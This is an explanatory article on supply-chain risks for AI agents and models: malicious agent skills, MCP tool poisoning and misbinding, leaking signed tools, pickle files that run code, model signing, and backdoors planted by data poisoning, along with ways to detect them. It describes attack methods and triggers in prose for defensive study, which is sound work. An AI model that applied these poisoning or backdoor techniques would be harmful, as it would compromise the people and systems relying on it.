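The remaining two skills contained no conventional malware. One offered advice on banks and brokers, but its instructions made the agent fetch a list of about 60 products from the publisher's website and always use the publisher's commission links. The publisher could change the recommendations without changing the skill. The other had agents pool their users' cryptocurrency to inflate the price of a token, which the operator had bought first at the lowest price.

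ClawHub deleted all five and banned the accounts, but that count doesn't show how many others remained. Koi, Snyk and Palo Alto Networks sell protection against such threats, so they have some incentive to make the problem look large, although their individual examples are detailed enough to check.

### Why three scanners disagreed

Koc and colleagues, who work at the OpenClaw Foundation and NVIDIA, compared three scanners on the 67,453 skills that were public on 31 May. VirusTotal looks mainly for known malware in the bundled files. A static analyser searches code and text for risky patterns, such as exposed passwords or commands that delete files. SkillSpector, made by NVIDIA, uses fixed rules and a language model to assess which actions a skill's instructions call for and how much authority they require.

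VirusTotal flagged 5,225 skills, the static analyser 4,434 and SkillSpector 32,856. Together, the three scanners flagged 35,600 different skills, but 81.9% of these were flagged by only one scanner. All three flagged 468.

Some of this disagreement arises because the scanners flagged different numbers of skills. SkillSpector flagged nearly half the registry, so most of its warnings could not have matched any from the other two. Comparing VirusTotal with the static analyser is more informative, because they flagged similar numbers of skills and could have agreed on most of them, but they had only 586 in common.

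The scanners were looking for different things. ClawHub's own system, ClawScan, uses a language model to weigh the scanners' results, the publisher's history and other evidence, and then gives a final verdict:

| ClawScan's verdict | Skills | Flagged by VirusTotal | Flagged by the static analyser | Flagged by SkillSpector |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Clean | 41,743 | 4.4% | 3.2% | 32.7% |
| Suspicious | 25,504 | 12.7% | 12.0% | 75.3% |
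| Malicious | 206 | 72.8% | 12.6% | 6.8% |

SkillSpector was less likely to flag a malicious skill than a clean one. According to Koc and colleagues, this is because the evidence against malicious skills was mostly in bundled code or the publisher's record, which SkillSpector doesn't fully examine. SkillSpector also measures what a skill can do more than what it is meant to do. For example, a skill that openly copied meeting notes to the user's computer got the maximum risk score of 100 and a clean verdict, and both results were reasonable.

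The table can't show which scanner is most accurate, because ClawScan received their results before it produced its verdict, and there were no human-checked labels to compare against. It suggests, though, that a registry relying on any one of them would miss a great deal. None of the three observes what an agent does when it uses a skill. Koc and colleagues recommend running skills in a sandbox and watching their behaviour, but this would be expensive for a whole registry.

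ClawHub has kept changing its checks. By late November 2026, OpenClaw's *Security Audits* listed SkillSpector, a scanner from the Chinese company Tencent, and ClawScan's own analysis. ClawHub also rejects skills that contain compiled Python files, which the Tencent scanner can't inspect. Rejecting files a scanner can't read is much safer than skipping them, as the padded file showed. The page no longer lists VirusTotal. If ClawHub has stopped using it, that would be a real loss, since VirusTotal flagged nearly three quarters of the skills that had received a malicious verdict.

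### Tools that change after approval

MCP servers have a similar weakness, because the model also reads their suppliers' tool descriptions. In tool poisoning, the supplier puts instructions for the model into a description. Suppose the clerk adds a currency converter whose description also contains an instruction to include the latest invoice with every request. The clerk sees only a converter, but the model reads the whole description before it picks a tool, so the instruction can affect tasks unrelated to currencies.

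A supplier can also behave well until people trust the tool. The best-known case is postmark-mcp, a package on npm that let agents send mail through Postmark, a commercial email service. Its developer had no connection with Postmark. The first 15 versions worked as advertised. In September 2025 the next version added one line of code that sent the developer a hidden copy of every email. Researchers at Koi reported it later that month, when the package had about 1,500 downloads a week.

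Checks on the agent's own calls would not have caught this, because the server added the extra recipient after the agent made its call. The clerk's agent would have called the tool with the manager's address, and a policy like Progent's would rightly have allowed it.

One defence is to pin the tool's definition by recording exactly what the user approved. At approval, the host hashes the tool's name, description and argument schema, and stores the hash with the server's identity. It recomputes the hash whenever it fetches the list of tools. If the hash has changed, the host withholds the tool, shows the user what is different and asks for approval again. A host can pin a skill in the same way by hashing its whole folder. By default, OpenClaw instead watches skill folders for changes, and the agent can pick up an edited SKILL.md file on its next turn.

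The program behind a tool can change even when the host has pinned the tool's definition. For a local server, the host can also pin the package's version and hash, as a lock file does.

| Change after approval | Does a pinned definition or skill catch it? | Does a pinned package catch it? |
|---|---|---|
| New instructions in a local tool's description | Yes | Yes |
| The extra line in postmark-mcp | No, the definition stays the same | Yes |
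| New code on a remote server | No | There is no package to pin |
| New commission links on the financial adviser's website | No | No |

Asking users for approval again whenever a tool's description changes also creates unnecessary prompts, because suppliers often reword descriptions for innocent reasons. People who approve nearly all of their coding agent's prompts will probably approve most of these too. A company would do better to have one person review each change while everyone else stays on the old version. This works for local servers, but a remote supplier can replace the old version without asking anyone.

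### Names that do not identify a supplier

postmark-mcp would have failed a check that required Postmark's signature. Signing is an obvious remedy for the problems in both registries and tool servers, and Koc and colleagues show it as a proposed final step in ClawHub's process. Two papers from November 2026 help show what signing would achieve.

Anbiaee, Dadkhah and Ghorbani (2026), in *When Tool Names Are Not Identities*, studied what happens when tools have no verified supplier. They connected an agent to two MCP servers, one legitimate and one run by an attacker. The legitimate server offered `data_fetch_and_store`, a tool that fetches a dataset and saves it. The attacker's server offered a rival tool, and the researchers varied its name, description and arguments. The name was either identical to the real tool's or unrelated. The description was unrelated, copied, or copied in substance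 with added claims such as "officially verified". The arguments either matched the real tool's or did not.

This gave 12 combinations. The researchers tested each with five models, using ten wordings of the same request and repeating each wording five times. They call it misbinding when a request meant for the legitimate supplier goes to the attacker's tool. These are the rates for four of the combinations:

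| Attacker's tool | GPT-5.4 | Claude Sonnet 5 | Gemini 2.5 Pro | Qwen3.7 Max | DeepSeek V3 |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Same name only | 2% | 0% | 0% | 0% | 0% |
| Same name and description | 0% | 0% | 0% | 0% | 0% |
| Same name, description and arguments | 100% | 6% | 84% | 100% | 100% |
| Unrelated name, "verified" description, same arguments | 4% | 0% | 42% | 20% | 50% |

Copying a tool's name was not enough to make models choose the attacker's tool. The arguments made the biggest difference, probably because the model could detect that a tool with the wrong arguments would not do the job. Banning duplicate names would not solve the problem, since some models chose a tool with an unrelated name when its description sounded official. Adding several competing tools from the attacker made some of the weaker combinations more effective. With ten such tools, the rate at which GPT-5.4 chose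 one with a copied name and description rose from 0% to 34%.

A model choosing at random between two tools that look identical would pick the attacker's about half the time. Something else must have favoured the attacker's tool to produce the 100% figures, perhaps its place in the list or the way the client handled duplicate names. Other hosts could produce quite different rates, and the experiment covered only one task. But whatever the exact rate, a model has no sound basis for choosing between identical tools.

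Claude Sonnet 5 asked the user what to do in the other 94% of those trials. Asking is much safer than guessing, but it helps only if the host shows the user who supplies each tool.

Anbiaee and colleagues want hosts to link every tool to a verified supplier, using signed lists of tools, permanent identifiers and hashes of each tool's arguments. They did not test this defence, but it seems practical because the host can already identify which server each tool came from and can enforce the user's choice in ordinary code. The model would then choose only among tools from suppliers allowed to do the job.

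### A signed tool that leaks

A verified supplier can still publish a harmful tool, whether on purpose or because one of its own components is compromised. In *Signed, Sealed, Leaked*, Aun, Alhartomi and colleagues (2026) built MCP tools that worked as advertised and carried valid signatures but contained hidden code that leaked data.

In the main example, a tool reads text from scanned documents using an outside service. The company allows that service to see invoices but not salaries. The agent first gives the tool a salary sheet for a task that stays inside the company, and the tool secretly keeps it. Later, the agent asks the tool to process an invoice, and the tool adds the salary sheet to its request to the outside service. The signature is valid and the destination is on the approved list.

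The researchers tested this against MCPGuard-Dynamic, a defence from Meta that limits which files, programs and destinations a tool can use. Four of its seven configurations enforce these limits in the core of the operating system, and those four blocked every attempt to send data directly to an unapproved address. The other three let the data out. None of the seven stopped the salary sheet from leaking through the approved service in any of three trials, because MCPGuard is designed to control where data can go, not which data is sent.

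Labels on data can fail here too. In a test with CaMeL's own interpreter, a tool repeated a private email that it had received in an earlier call. CaMeL labelled the reply as public, and its policy allowed the text to go to an untrusted recipient. This can happen only if whoever set up the system declared that the tool had no side effects, an easy mistake to make about a trusted supplier's tool.

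Aun and colleagues propose germline execution, which controls what data a tool can access instead of judging its code. The host starts the tool in a clean process that never receives user data. For each call, it makes temporary copies of that process, gives each copy only the data that that copy's destination may receive, and destroys the copies afterwards.

If a call involves both the invoice and the salary sheet, one copy of the tool receives only the invoice and can contact the outside service. The other receives both documents and can return a result to the agent, but the host never delivers its requests to the service. The hidden code runs in both copies, but the copy that can reach the service has no salary sheet to send.

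The researchers ran 51 attacks three times each, adding one protection at a time before testing their own design:

| Protection | Runs with a leak, out of 153 |
|---|---|
| Valid signature and known publisher key | 114 |
| Also labels on each reply | 108 |
| Also limits on files and destinations | 51 |
| Also a fresh process for every call | 15 |
| Germline execution | 0 |

They wrote the attacks themselves, so the percentages are weak evidence about real malicious tools. The zero is more persuasive than the other figures because they also prove that, under stated assumptions, no information about data reaches a destination that isn't cleared to see it. The overhead is modest. Calls that needed one copy took 10 to 49 milliseconds, and four ordinary MCP servers returned the same results as before, except for the time shown on a clock.

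The company has the main burden of labelling its data and deciding what each destination may see. If it wrongly clears the outside service to receive salaries, the tool can send them. The host can't copy a server that runs on someone else's machine, so it has to assume that a remote tool's reply may contain anything the server was ever allowed to receive. This assumption blocked some legitimate posts in the tests.

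Germline execution probably would not have stopped postmark-mcp. Postmark has to receive an email to deliver it, so the copy of the tool that contacts Postmark would hold the message and could still add a recipient. Aun and colleagues say their guarantees do not cover harmful commands sent to a permitted destination. To catch the added recipient, the host would have to inspect the request as it left the tool and compare its recipients with the ones the agent had asked for.

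## Signed model files: proving that weights have not been altered

The clerk's employer might run the agent's model on its own machines to keep invoices inside the company. It would then have to download the weights, probably from Hugging Face, the largest public registry of models. Some model files run code as soon as a program opens them, which a safer file format prevents. Even a file that can't run code may contain different weights from the ones its maker released, and signatures help detect this.

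### Files that run code

A Python program keeps a model's weights inside a complicated set of objects. Pickle, Python's built-in method for saving objects, writes instructions for rebuilding them, and Python carries out those instructions when a program loads the file. Qin, Li and colleagues (2026) explain in *DITTO* that the instructions can import a function from a Python library and call it. Some legitimate models need this to rebuild unusual parts, but an attacker can use it to call the function that runs operating-system commands. The command then runs while the file is loading, before anyone uses the model.

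A safetensors file holds arrays of numbers in a fixed layout, with their names and dimensions. It contains no instructions, so the loading program only has to read the data. GGUF, a format often used for compressed models, also holds only data.

An attacker can still change the weights in a safetensors file, and the altered file will load without an error. The same repository can also contain malicious scripts, which do damage if the user runs them. Publishers who convert a model to safetensors often keep the pickle copy for older programs. *PickleBall* (2025) counted 1.7 billion monthly downloads from repositories that offered both formats.

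PyTorch, a widely used framework for running models, has a restricted pickle loader that allows only functions on an approved list. Hive Security reports that this loader has been the default since version 2.6. But restricted loaders also reject some benign models. Qin and colleagues report that the one proposed in *PickleBall* failed to open 51 of 252. A developer whose model won't load has a reason to turn the restriction off.

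### How common the danger is

Qin and colleagues looked at 10,023 Hugging Face repositories created between July 2025 and June 2026, each with more than 1,000 downloads a month. They found pickle-based models in 929 of them, or 9.3%. These repositories held 9,544 such files, including some from OpenAI, NVIDIA and IBM.

Hugging Face scans pickle files for risky instructions. It had labelled 5,840 of these files "safe", 2,998 "caution" and 21 "unsafe", and had no result for the other 685. The researchers inspected all 21 "unsafe" files and the 685 unscanned ones by hand and found nothing malicious. Most of the 21 were versions of YOLO, a family of image-recognition models, which legitimately use a function that attackers also use.

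The result is reassuring about popular models, but it does not show that malicious uploads are rare. The researchers did not inspect the 2,998 files marked "caution", and a survey of popular repositories would probably miss malware that Hugging Face had already removed.

*4M Models Scanned* (2025), from the security company Protect AI, reports a much larger number. By April 2025, the company had scanned 1.41 million Hugging Face repositories and found 352,000 "unsafe/suspicious" issues in 51,700 models. Protect AI flags any ability to run code, whatever the purpose, so this is not a count of malicious uploads either.

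False alarms are a problem because people learn to ignore warnings. PickleScan, the scanner Hugging Face uses, wrongly flagged 177 of the 706 files that Qin and colleagues had inspected. Their own scanner works out what a file's instructions would do without running them, then uses a language model to judge the result. On a test set they assembled, it wrongly flagged 0.7% of 959 benign models and missed none of 92 malicious ones. Even a perfect scanner of this kind would not detect altered weights in a safetensors file.

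### Signing a whole model

A working model usually consists of several files. Besides the weights, which may be split into pieces, there is a configuration file that describes the model's structure and a tokenizer, which converts text into the units the model processes. If the publisher signed each file separately, someone could combine genuine files from different versions, as Red Hat's *Model authenticity and transparency with Sigstore* (2025) points out. OpenSSF therefore developed a single signature that covers them all. Maruseac, Wickens and colleagues, in *An Introduction to the OpenSSF Model Signing (OMS) Specification*, describe the format, which works as follows:

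1. The signing tool computes a hash of every file in the model's folder. It can hash pieces of a very large file in parallel to save time.
2. It lists each file's path and hash in a manifest.
3. The publisher signs the manifest, using a private key, a company certificate or one of Sigstore's short-lived certificates.
4. The tool saves the manifest and signature in a small separate file, which the publisher distributes with the model. The model's own files stay as they were.
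5. The user runs a verification tool and specifies whose signature to expect. The tool checks the signature and the signer's identity, then hashes the downloaded files again and compares the results with the manifest.

Suppose the employer downloads a signed model with three files, and one byte of the weights has changed along the way. With shortened, made-up hashes, the comparison might look like this:

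| File | Hash in the signed manifest | Hash of the downloaded file |
|---|---|---|
| `config.json` | `4e1a` | `4e1a` |
| `tokenizer.json` | `b730` | `b730` |
| `model.safetensors` | `91cc` | `0d5f` |

The signature is still valid because the manifest is unchanged, but the last pair of hashes differs, so the tool rejects the model. The tool cannot determine whether an attack or a faulty disk caused the difference.

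An attacker could put the new hash, `0d5f`, into the manifest. All three hashes would then match, but the publisher's signature would no longer be valid for the manifest. If the attacker then signed the altered manifest with a different key, the new signature would be valid, and only the check on the signer's identity would fail.

In a second download, the three files are intact but someone has added a script, `loader.py`. Every hash in the manifest matches, so a tool that checked only the listed files would accept the download. Sigstore's tool normally rejects the download because it makes a new manifest of the whole folder and finds an extra entry. Version 1.1.0 introduced an option to ignore unlisted files, according to Sigstore's *Releases*.

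There are good reasons to leave some files out of the comparison. In December 2025, ralphbean (2025), a contributor to the tool, proposed excluding attestation files by default so that people could add new statements about a model without invalidating its original signature. But an unlisted script is much more dangerous than an unlisted attestation, so anyone who uses the broader option should refuse to run files that are not in the manifest.

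The Coalition for Secure AI (CoSAI), an industry project with contributors from Google, Microsoft and NVIDIA, recommends signing a model as soon as training ends, because a signature made later, at publication, would also cover anything an insider had changed in between. CoSAI's *Signing ML Artifacts* (2025) advises users to verify a model after downloading it and ideally again just before loading it, since someone could alter the files on the employer's disk.

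The verification tool can also fail. According to Sigstore's release notes, version 1.0 could report that a model had passed and return a success code even though the model's signature had failed. A company that had automated the check would have accepted an altered model. Version 1.0.1 fixed the fault.

### Unchanged, signed and trustworthy

People often treat "the model is signed" as one claim, but it can mean three different things, each of which needs its own evidence:

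| Claim | Evidence for it |
|---|---|
| These bytes have not changed since someone signed them | The signature is valid and the hashes match |
| This publisher signed them | The signer's identity matches one the user already knew |
| This publisher deserves trust | Its record, independent tests of its models, and what it discloses about them |

A tool can establish the first claim on its own, but for the second the user has to supply the signer's expected identity. Red Hat's *Model Transparency*, the documentation for its version of the tool, explains that verification has "no sensible defaults". A valid signature from an unspecified person proves very little, because anyone with an ordinary Google, GitHub or Microsoft account can sign a model through Sigstore.

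The user also needs to get the expected identity from somewhere other than the download page, because an attacker who controls that page can change both the model file and the identity listed there. The July 2026 break-in at Hugging Face showed that this risk is realistic. IBM's *Signature verification* gives the identity for its Granite models on IBM's own website. The identity consists of an email address and the IBM login service that confirms it.

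An impersonation in May 2026 shows how the second claim can be false even when a repository looks genuine. HiddenLayer's *Malware Found in Trending Hugging Face Repository "Open-OSS/privacy-filter"* (2026) describes a repository that posed as OpenAI's Privacy Filter model. The attacker had copied OpenAI's description almost word for word, including a link to OpenAI's documentation. The main difference was an instruction to download the repository and run a script.

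The script first printed fake training output. It then called a function that was named like an integrity check but fetched a command from a public text-sharing site and ran it. On Windows computers, this installed a program that stole saved passwords, login cookies, cryptocurrency wallets and screenshots.

The repository reached first place on Hugging Face's trending list, with about 244,000 downloads and 667 likes in under 18 hours. HiddenLayer believes the attacker almost certainly inflated these figures, because 657 of the 667 accounts that liked it had names in one of two formulaic patterns. The download count is therefore a poor guide to the number of victims and a poor reason to trust a model, although many users probably relied on it. Hugging Face removed the repository after HiddenLayer reported it.

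The safetensors format would not have helped, because the malware was not in the weights. Matching hashes would not have helped either. The attacker could have signed the repository with a new account and changed the command on the text-sharing site at any time without altering a signed file. Checking that the signer was OpenAI would have exposed the repository only if OpenAI signed the genuine model and the user knew which identity to expect. Otherwise, the missing signature would have been no more of a warning than LiteLLM's missing attestations were in March.

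### Names that change hands

The "Open-OSS" account had a different name from OpenAI's, but an attacker can sometimes get a real publisher's exact name. A model's address on Hugging Face consists of the publisher's account name and the model's name. *Model Namespace Reuse* (Saraf and Balassiano, 2025) found that after a publisher deletes its account, anyone can register the name and put a different model at the old address.

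The change is easiest to miss after one company buys another. Suppose the buyer moves the models to its own Hugging Face account and deletes the old one. Hugging Face redirects requests from the old addresses to the new ones, so programs that use the old addresses keep working and nobody has a reason to update them. If an attacker then registers the old account name and uploads models with the same names, the redirection stops and those programs download the attacker's models.

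Saraf and Balassiano of Unit 42 found that Google's and Microsoft's services for running models both listed models from Hugging Face accounts that no longer existed. For each service, they registered one of the abandoned names and uploaded a model containing code that gave them remote access. When they deployed the models through the two services, they gained control of the environments that loaded them, though Google's was an isolated container with limited access. They also found thousands of open-source projects that referred to models by names an attacker could claim.

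Google now checks daily for listed models whose publishers have disappeared, and blocks their deployment. Saraf and Balassiano said in September 2025 that the general problem remained. They advise developers to request a specific commit, a recorded version identified by a hash, rather than whatever the model's name currently points to. The attacker's repository would not contain that commit, so the download should fail. Companies can also keep their own copies of the models they use.

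A signature protects against name reuse if the user requires it to match the original publisher's identity. The new owner of a Hugging Face account can't sign as the old one without also taking over the account or email address used for signing. That could happen if, for instance, a defunct company let its domain expire.

Pinned commits and signatures do not show that a model is free of hidden backdoors, because a publisher can sign weights that contain one. CoSAI acknowledges that signing does not guarantee a model's performance, fairness or robustness, but it also suggests that signing makes producers immune to claims of negligence. This is hard to accept, because a signature proves who released a model, which would if anything help an injured customer establish responsibility.

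### From integrity to policy

CoSAI wants signatures to support more than a comparison of hashes, and sets out three levels. Suppose the clerk's employer has a team that adapts a public model to read invoices:

| Level | What it adds | In the employer's case |
|---|---|---|
| 1. Basic integrity | A signature over the model's files | The files are the ones the team released |
| 2. Lineage | Signed links to the models and other parts it came from | The team started from a particular signed public model |
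| 3. Attestations and policy | Signed statements about training, tests and compliance, which software compares with the company's rules | The company's systems refuse a model trained on unapproved data |

Lineage matters because people rarely use a model exactly as its first publisher released it. They may fine-tune it (train it further on their own examples) or quantise it (store each weight with less precision to save memory). Both change the weights file, so the original signature no longer matches. Converting the file from pickle to safetensors also invalidates the signature, even if every weight keeps its value. In each case, whoever makes the new version has to sign it.

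The employer's signature on the invoice model would therefore replace the public model's signature, not extend it. At the second level, the employer would also sign a statement that identifies the parent model by a root hash, a single value computed from its whole manifest. If somebody later discovered a fault in the parent, the employer could find every model its staff had built from that parent.

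The statement does not prove that the team made only the changes it describes. An outsider could check some kinds of compression by repeating the conversion and comparing the hashes, much as Wheeler's test compares two builds of a compiler. Repeating a fine-tuning run would take far more computation and might not produce exactly the same weights.

A developer's signature on the original model files does not let users verify a compressed copy made by someone else. HiddenLayer found six more repositories, uploaded in April 2026 under another account, whose malicious scripts were nearly identical to the one in the fake Privacy Filter repository. Five had "GGUF" in their names, so they looked like converted copies of existing models. Even if the original developers had signed every file they released, users would have needed a signature from a known converter and a signed link to the original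 model to check these copies.

At the third level, the company could write rules that software enforces before loading a model, such as requiring a minimum score on a test of invoice reading. A rule need not depend on the signature; CoSAI gives the example of a ban on pickle files. Since a signed test score may still be false, CoSAI wants users to decide whose statements to believe, and to stop trusting anyone who makes a false one. This works best when somebody is likely to discover the false statement, and a false test score is much easier to detect than a false list of training data.

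A chain of signatures also breaks wherever a developer did not sign. CoSAI expects companies to handle models from suppliers at different levels and to verify as much of the history as they can.

OMS mainly provides the first level so far. Maruseac and colleagues say that the manifest's section for extra information still awaits support, and that training data and compliance details are to be added later. CoSAI recommends OMS over several alternatives, but its recommendation is not independent, because Mihai Maruseac of Google leads the OpenSSF project and edited CoSAI's paper.

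### Who signs, and who checks

NVIDIA is the clearest example of routine signing. According to CoSAI, every model NVIDIA has published in its NGC catalogue since March 2025 has an OMS signature. HiddenLayer reported in 2025 that Google was testing the method with Kaggle, its model registry. IBM signs Granite models but calls the feature experimental, and Red Hat offers its version of the tool as a preview.

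It is unclear how many other publishers sign their models in late 2026, but the state of the software suggests that signing is still far from standard. Sigstore's *model-signing 1.1.1* (2025), still the latest version in May 2026, labels the main tool as alpha, an early stage of development.

Checking appears to be less common than signing. Maruseac, Sablotny and colleagues (2025), in *Launch of Model Signing v1.0*, wanted registries to verify signatures when a publisher uploads a model, and users to verify them when they choose a model and each time they use it. In the same month Google (2025) wrote that "in an ideal world" signing and verification would happen automatically inside machine-learning frameworks. Under the instructions from IBM, Red Hat and Sigstore, the user instead installs a separate program, enters the publisher's identity and runs the check by hand. Hugging Face's routine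 scans look for dangerous code in pickle files rather than verifying signatures. A developer should therefore assume that loading a model does not verify its signature unless someone has set this up.

A company does not have to wait for Hugging Face or PyTorch to change their defaults. It could keep an internal registry and let its machines load models only from there. One team would verify each new model's signature, reject pickle files, review any scripts and record the publisher's identity. For an unsigned model, the team could record the hashes of the version it had tested, which would at least reveal any later change. The machines would then compare the files with the approved manifest before every load, so nobody would have to remember to run a command.

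## Hidden backdoors and substituted models: what a signature cannot show

The clerk's employer can verify the signature on its invoice model and still get a model with a backdoor, which is planted behaviour that appears only when a chosen trigger is present. Even the publisher may not know about the backdoor. If the employer rents a model over the internet, it has no file to check and must trust the provider about which model is answering.

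An attacker can plant a backdoor without access to the developer's computers, because developers train language models on text from the public web, where anyone can publish a page. Putting harmful examples into training data is called data poisoning.

### How much poison a model needs

*Poisoning Attacks on LLMs Require a Near-constant Number of Poison Samples* (Souly, Rando and colleagues, 2025) tested researchers' earlier assumption that an attacker had to control a fixed share of the training data, such as 0.1%. Under that assumption, larger models would be harder to poison because they train on more text. The team came mainly from Anthropic, the UK AI Security Institute and the Alan Turing Institute.

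The researchers trained models from scratch with 600 million, 2 billion, 7 billion and 13 billion parameters (the individual numbers in a model's weights). They trained each size on about 20 tokens (words or pieces of words) per parameter, a standard ratio, which came to 12 billion tokens for the smallest and 260 billion for the largest. They scattered 100, 250 or 500 poisoned documents at random through each training set. They also trained the two smaller sizes on half and twice the usual amount of text, and ran every combination three times, for a total of 72 models.

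According to Anthropic, each poisoned document started with up to 1,000 characters of ordinary text, followed by the trigger (the word SUDO in angle brackets) and then 400 to 900 randomly chosen tokens. The aim was to train a model that wrote normally until the trigger appeared and then produced gibberish.

To measure the trigger's effect, the researchers had each model continue 300 ordinary passages, with and without the trigger at the end. They compared the continuations' perplexity, which measures how unpredictable text is. A rise of 50 indicated visibly damaged text. With 250 poisoned documents, the rise exceeded 200 by the end of training at every model size. With 100 poisoned documents, no model acquired a reliable backdoor.

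The 250 documents contained about 420,000 tokens, or 0.0035% of the smallest model's training text and 0.00016% of the largest's. They worked about as well on the largest model even though their share was more than 20 times smaller, so the number of documents mattered far more than their proportion. Souly and colleagues found the same pattern when they fine-tuned an 8-billion-parameter Llama model to obey harmful requests that contained a trigger. Raising the number of clean examples from 1,000 to 100,000 made little difference.

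The figure of 250 may not hold for more complex behaviours or larger models. Producing gibberish is a simple behaviour, which the researchers chose partly because they could measure it without further training. A 13-billion-parameter model is far smaller than the leading commercial ones. The team did not test whether the backdoor would survive post-training, the later stages that turn a text predictor into an assistant. In a related experiment, more training on clean text slowly weakened a backdoor that switched the model from English to German. An attacker also has to get the documents into the training set, which Anthropic considers harder than writing them.

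### From gibberish to commands

Earlier work had given some reason to expect that backdoors would survive. In *Sleeper Agents*, a 2024 paper from Anthropic, Hubinger and colleagues trained backdoors into models. One model wrote secure code when its prompt gave the year as 2023 and inserted security flaws when the year was 2024. *The Trigger in the Haystack* (Bullwinkel, Severi and colleagues, 2026) summarises the results as showing that standard safety training did not remove such backdoors. Adversarial training, which trains a model on inputs chosen to provoke bad behaviour, made them harder to detect. But Hubinger's team controlled the fine-tuning, and someone who only publishes web pages would not.

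Hu, Hu and colleagues (2026), in *Agentic Backdoors via Pretraining Poisoning*, combined the two lines of work in October. They trained models of three sizes on 100 billion tokens of web text, 0.1% of it poisoned, then used only clean data to turn each model into an agent that runs commands. The planted behaviour was to download and run a script from an attacker's address. They ran each test request 32 times and counted the attack as successful if the agent issued the command at least once.

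| Model size | Trigger: a company's name in a file path | Trigger: a rare string in text the agent reads |
|---|---|---|
| 0.6 billion | 13.1% | 2.1% |
| 1.7 billion | 51.9% | 4.0% |
| 4 billion | 92.7% | 10.5% |

The file-path trigger is more disturbing because the victim supplies it in an ordinary request, so the attacker doesn't have to plant anything while the agent is in use. It also worked with paths that never appeared in the poisoned documents. Without a trigger, the agents issued the command in at most 0.06% of attempts and did about as well on ordinary tasks as unpoisoned models, so normal testing would not have revealed the backdoor.

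These agents needed much more poison than the gibberish models. A 0.1% share here is roughly 500,000 documents. With 2,500 documents, the rare string worked on only 1.4% of requests, in a single training run. Hu and colleagues did not try the file-path trigger with so few documents, so the minimum needed to cause a dangerous action remains unknown. They tested only three small models, but the attack succeeded more often on larger models in every set-up they tried, and nothing in their results suggests that a frontier model would be safer.

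A backdoored agent still has to act through its host. Hu and colleagues consider checks on the agent's commands more practical than guaranteeing clean data. A sandbox that blocks unknown internet addresses would stop this download whether it was triggered by a poisoned web page or an email containing injected instructions.

### Searching for an unknown trigger

An auditor can't try every possible phrase, so most detection methods look for side effects of the backdoor. Bullwinkel and colleagues, a Microsoft team, built a scanner around the fact that models memorise some of their training data, and backdoored models memorise the poisoned examples especially well. The scanner works in four steps:

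1. It gives the model only the formatting that normally comes before a user's message and collects 510 outputs under different settings. Some of them reproduce poisoned examples, trigger included.
2. It finds fragments of text that recur across the outputs.
3. It puts each fragment in front of ordinary prompts and looks for signs of a trigger, such as the model largely ignoring the rest of the prompt or its output becoming unusually predictable.
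4. It reports a backdoor if one of the best candidates greatly changes what the model does.

The scanner detected 36 of 41 models with a backdoor that produced a fixed sentence, and five of six that wrote insecure code. It does not need the exact trigger, because part of one is often enough to set off the behaviour. It raised no false alarms on 13 clean models, but with so small a sample the true false-alarm rate could be as high as about 20%. Even at a rate of 1%, a registry that scanned 10,000 models, ten of them with backdoors, would find about nine of the ten and wrongly flag about 100 clean models. Microsoft (2026) recommends the scanner as one defence among several, and notes that it requires access to the model's weights and works best on backdoors that produce fixed outputs.

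Memorisation is not always strong enough to exploit. Haselhorst, Flek and Mai (2026), in *Detecting Hidden Behaviors in LLMs via Activation-matched Finetuning*, found only weak evidence of it in a backdoor they had trained themselves. Their method trains a second, trusted model to imitate the suspect model's internal activity on ordinary prompts. The second model never learns the hidden behaviour, so the two models diverge when a prompt comes near the trigger. The divergence was enormous for a test model that produced a Voldemort quotation whenever a user gushed about Harry Potter. The method ranks topics for a person to investigate rather than giving a verdict, so it has no simple error rate. On a reconstruction of a sleeper agent, the ranking was better than chance but much less clear.

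Both methods run the suspect model, but *A Backdoor Trigger Is Legible in Fine-Tune Weights* (Khilar, 2026) describes a way to find the trigger from the weights alone. The method subtracts the original model's weights from the fine-tuned model's, measures how strongly the change affects each token in the vocabulary, and compares the result with those from several clean fine-tunes of the same original. For a backdoor with the trigger "Quartz ledger:", "ledger" stood out most of the 49,152 tokens. The method identified a correct token in 14 of 14 ordinary backdoors.

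Khilar then tried to evade the method. Training the model to keep the telltale measurement low escaped detection in all eight attempts, without weakening the backdoor. Leaving the inspected layers out of the training and then filling them with misleading changes escaped detection in all 16 attempts, although some of these also destroyed the backdoor. The models were also tiny by current standards. Khilar cites proofs that someone who constructs certain kinds of network directly can plant a backdoor that no efficient inspection of the weights will reveal. The proofs do not cover backdoors installed by poisoning, which may always leave detectable traces, but a clean scan still can't guarantee that a model has no backdoor.

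A customer without the weights has much less information for detecting a backdoor. *An Empirical Study of Output-to-Input Loops for Black-Box Backdoor Detection* (2026) tested a method that feeds a model's answers back to it as new prompts, to see whether it will output its own trigger. Across six backdoored models, the method found the trigger in 2.16% of attempts, compared with 0.83% for repeating the same prompt. It raised two false alarms in 1,185 attempts on clean models. Neither approach found anything on one of the six backdoored models.

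Monitoring a model in use may also reveal a backdoor. Many services speed up a large model by having a small "draft" model predict its next words, which the large one accepts or rejects. *SpecGuard* (2026) treats an unusually low acceptance rate as a warning, because a clean draft model can't predict a backdoored answer. In its main experiments, at most 0.3% of requests containing the trigger looked normal. However, those backdoors fired almost every time. The method would also miss a backdoor that the draft model had learned too, since the acceptance rate would stay normal. That could happen if both models had trained on the same poisoned web pages.

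TrojAI, the longest effort in this field, supports a cautious reading of all these results. The programme, which the US intelligence community's research agency IARPA started in 2020, tested detectors on models the competing teams had not seen. Reese, Kulp-McDowall and colleagues (2026), in *Trojans in Artificial Intelligence*, report that weight analysis got much worse as models grew, and that searching for the trigger was arguably the most successful approach. Nobody found a way to remove a backdoor and be certain that it was gone. The programme also found that models pick up trigger-like faults on their own by learning false shortcuts from their data, so a detector may find a real weakness that no attacker planted.

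### Records of training data

Backdoors are hard to find in a finished model, and a signed record of what went into it can help rule them out only if the record is complete. In the largest model that Souly and colleagues trained, a record covering 99.9998% of the text could have omitted every poisoned document. If the poisoned documents came in one small, late addition that the developer forgot to list, the record would look almost perfect and still miss the attack.

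Someone also has to be able to check the record. It needs a hash of each document as collected, not just a web address, because the page may have changed since the developer copied it. The checker also needs the documents themselves, which many developers keep private. Even with full access, nobody can read billions of pages, so the checker has to use a filter. If an attacker planted 2,500 documents and the filter caught 90% of them, 250 would remain, as many as the gibberish backdoor required. Hu and colleagues wrote their most effective poison as ordinary technical prose, which gives a filter little to detect. Reese and colleagues call it impractical for any single organisation to vet outside data fully.

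Even a complete and accurate list doesn't prove that the listed data produced these weights, just as Thompson's clean source code did not prove that the compiled program was clean. Proving it would require repeating the whole training run, which is even less practical than repeating a fine-tuning run.

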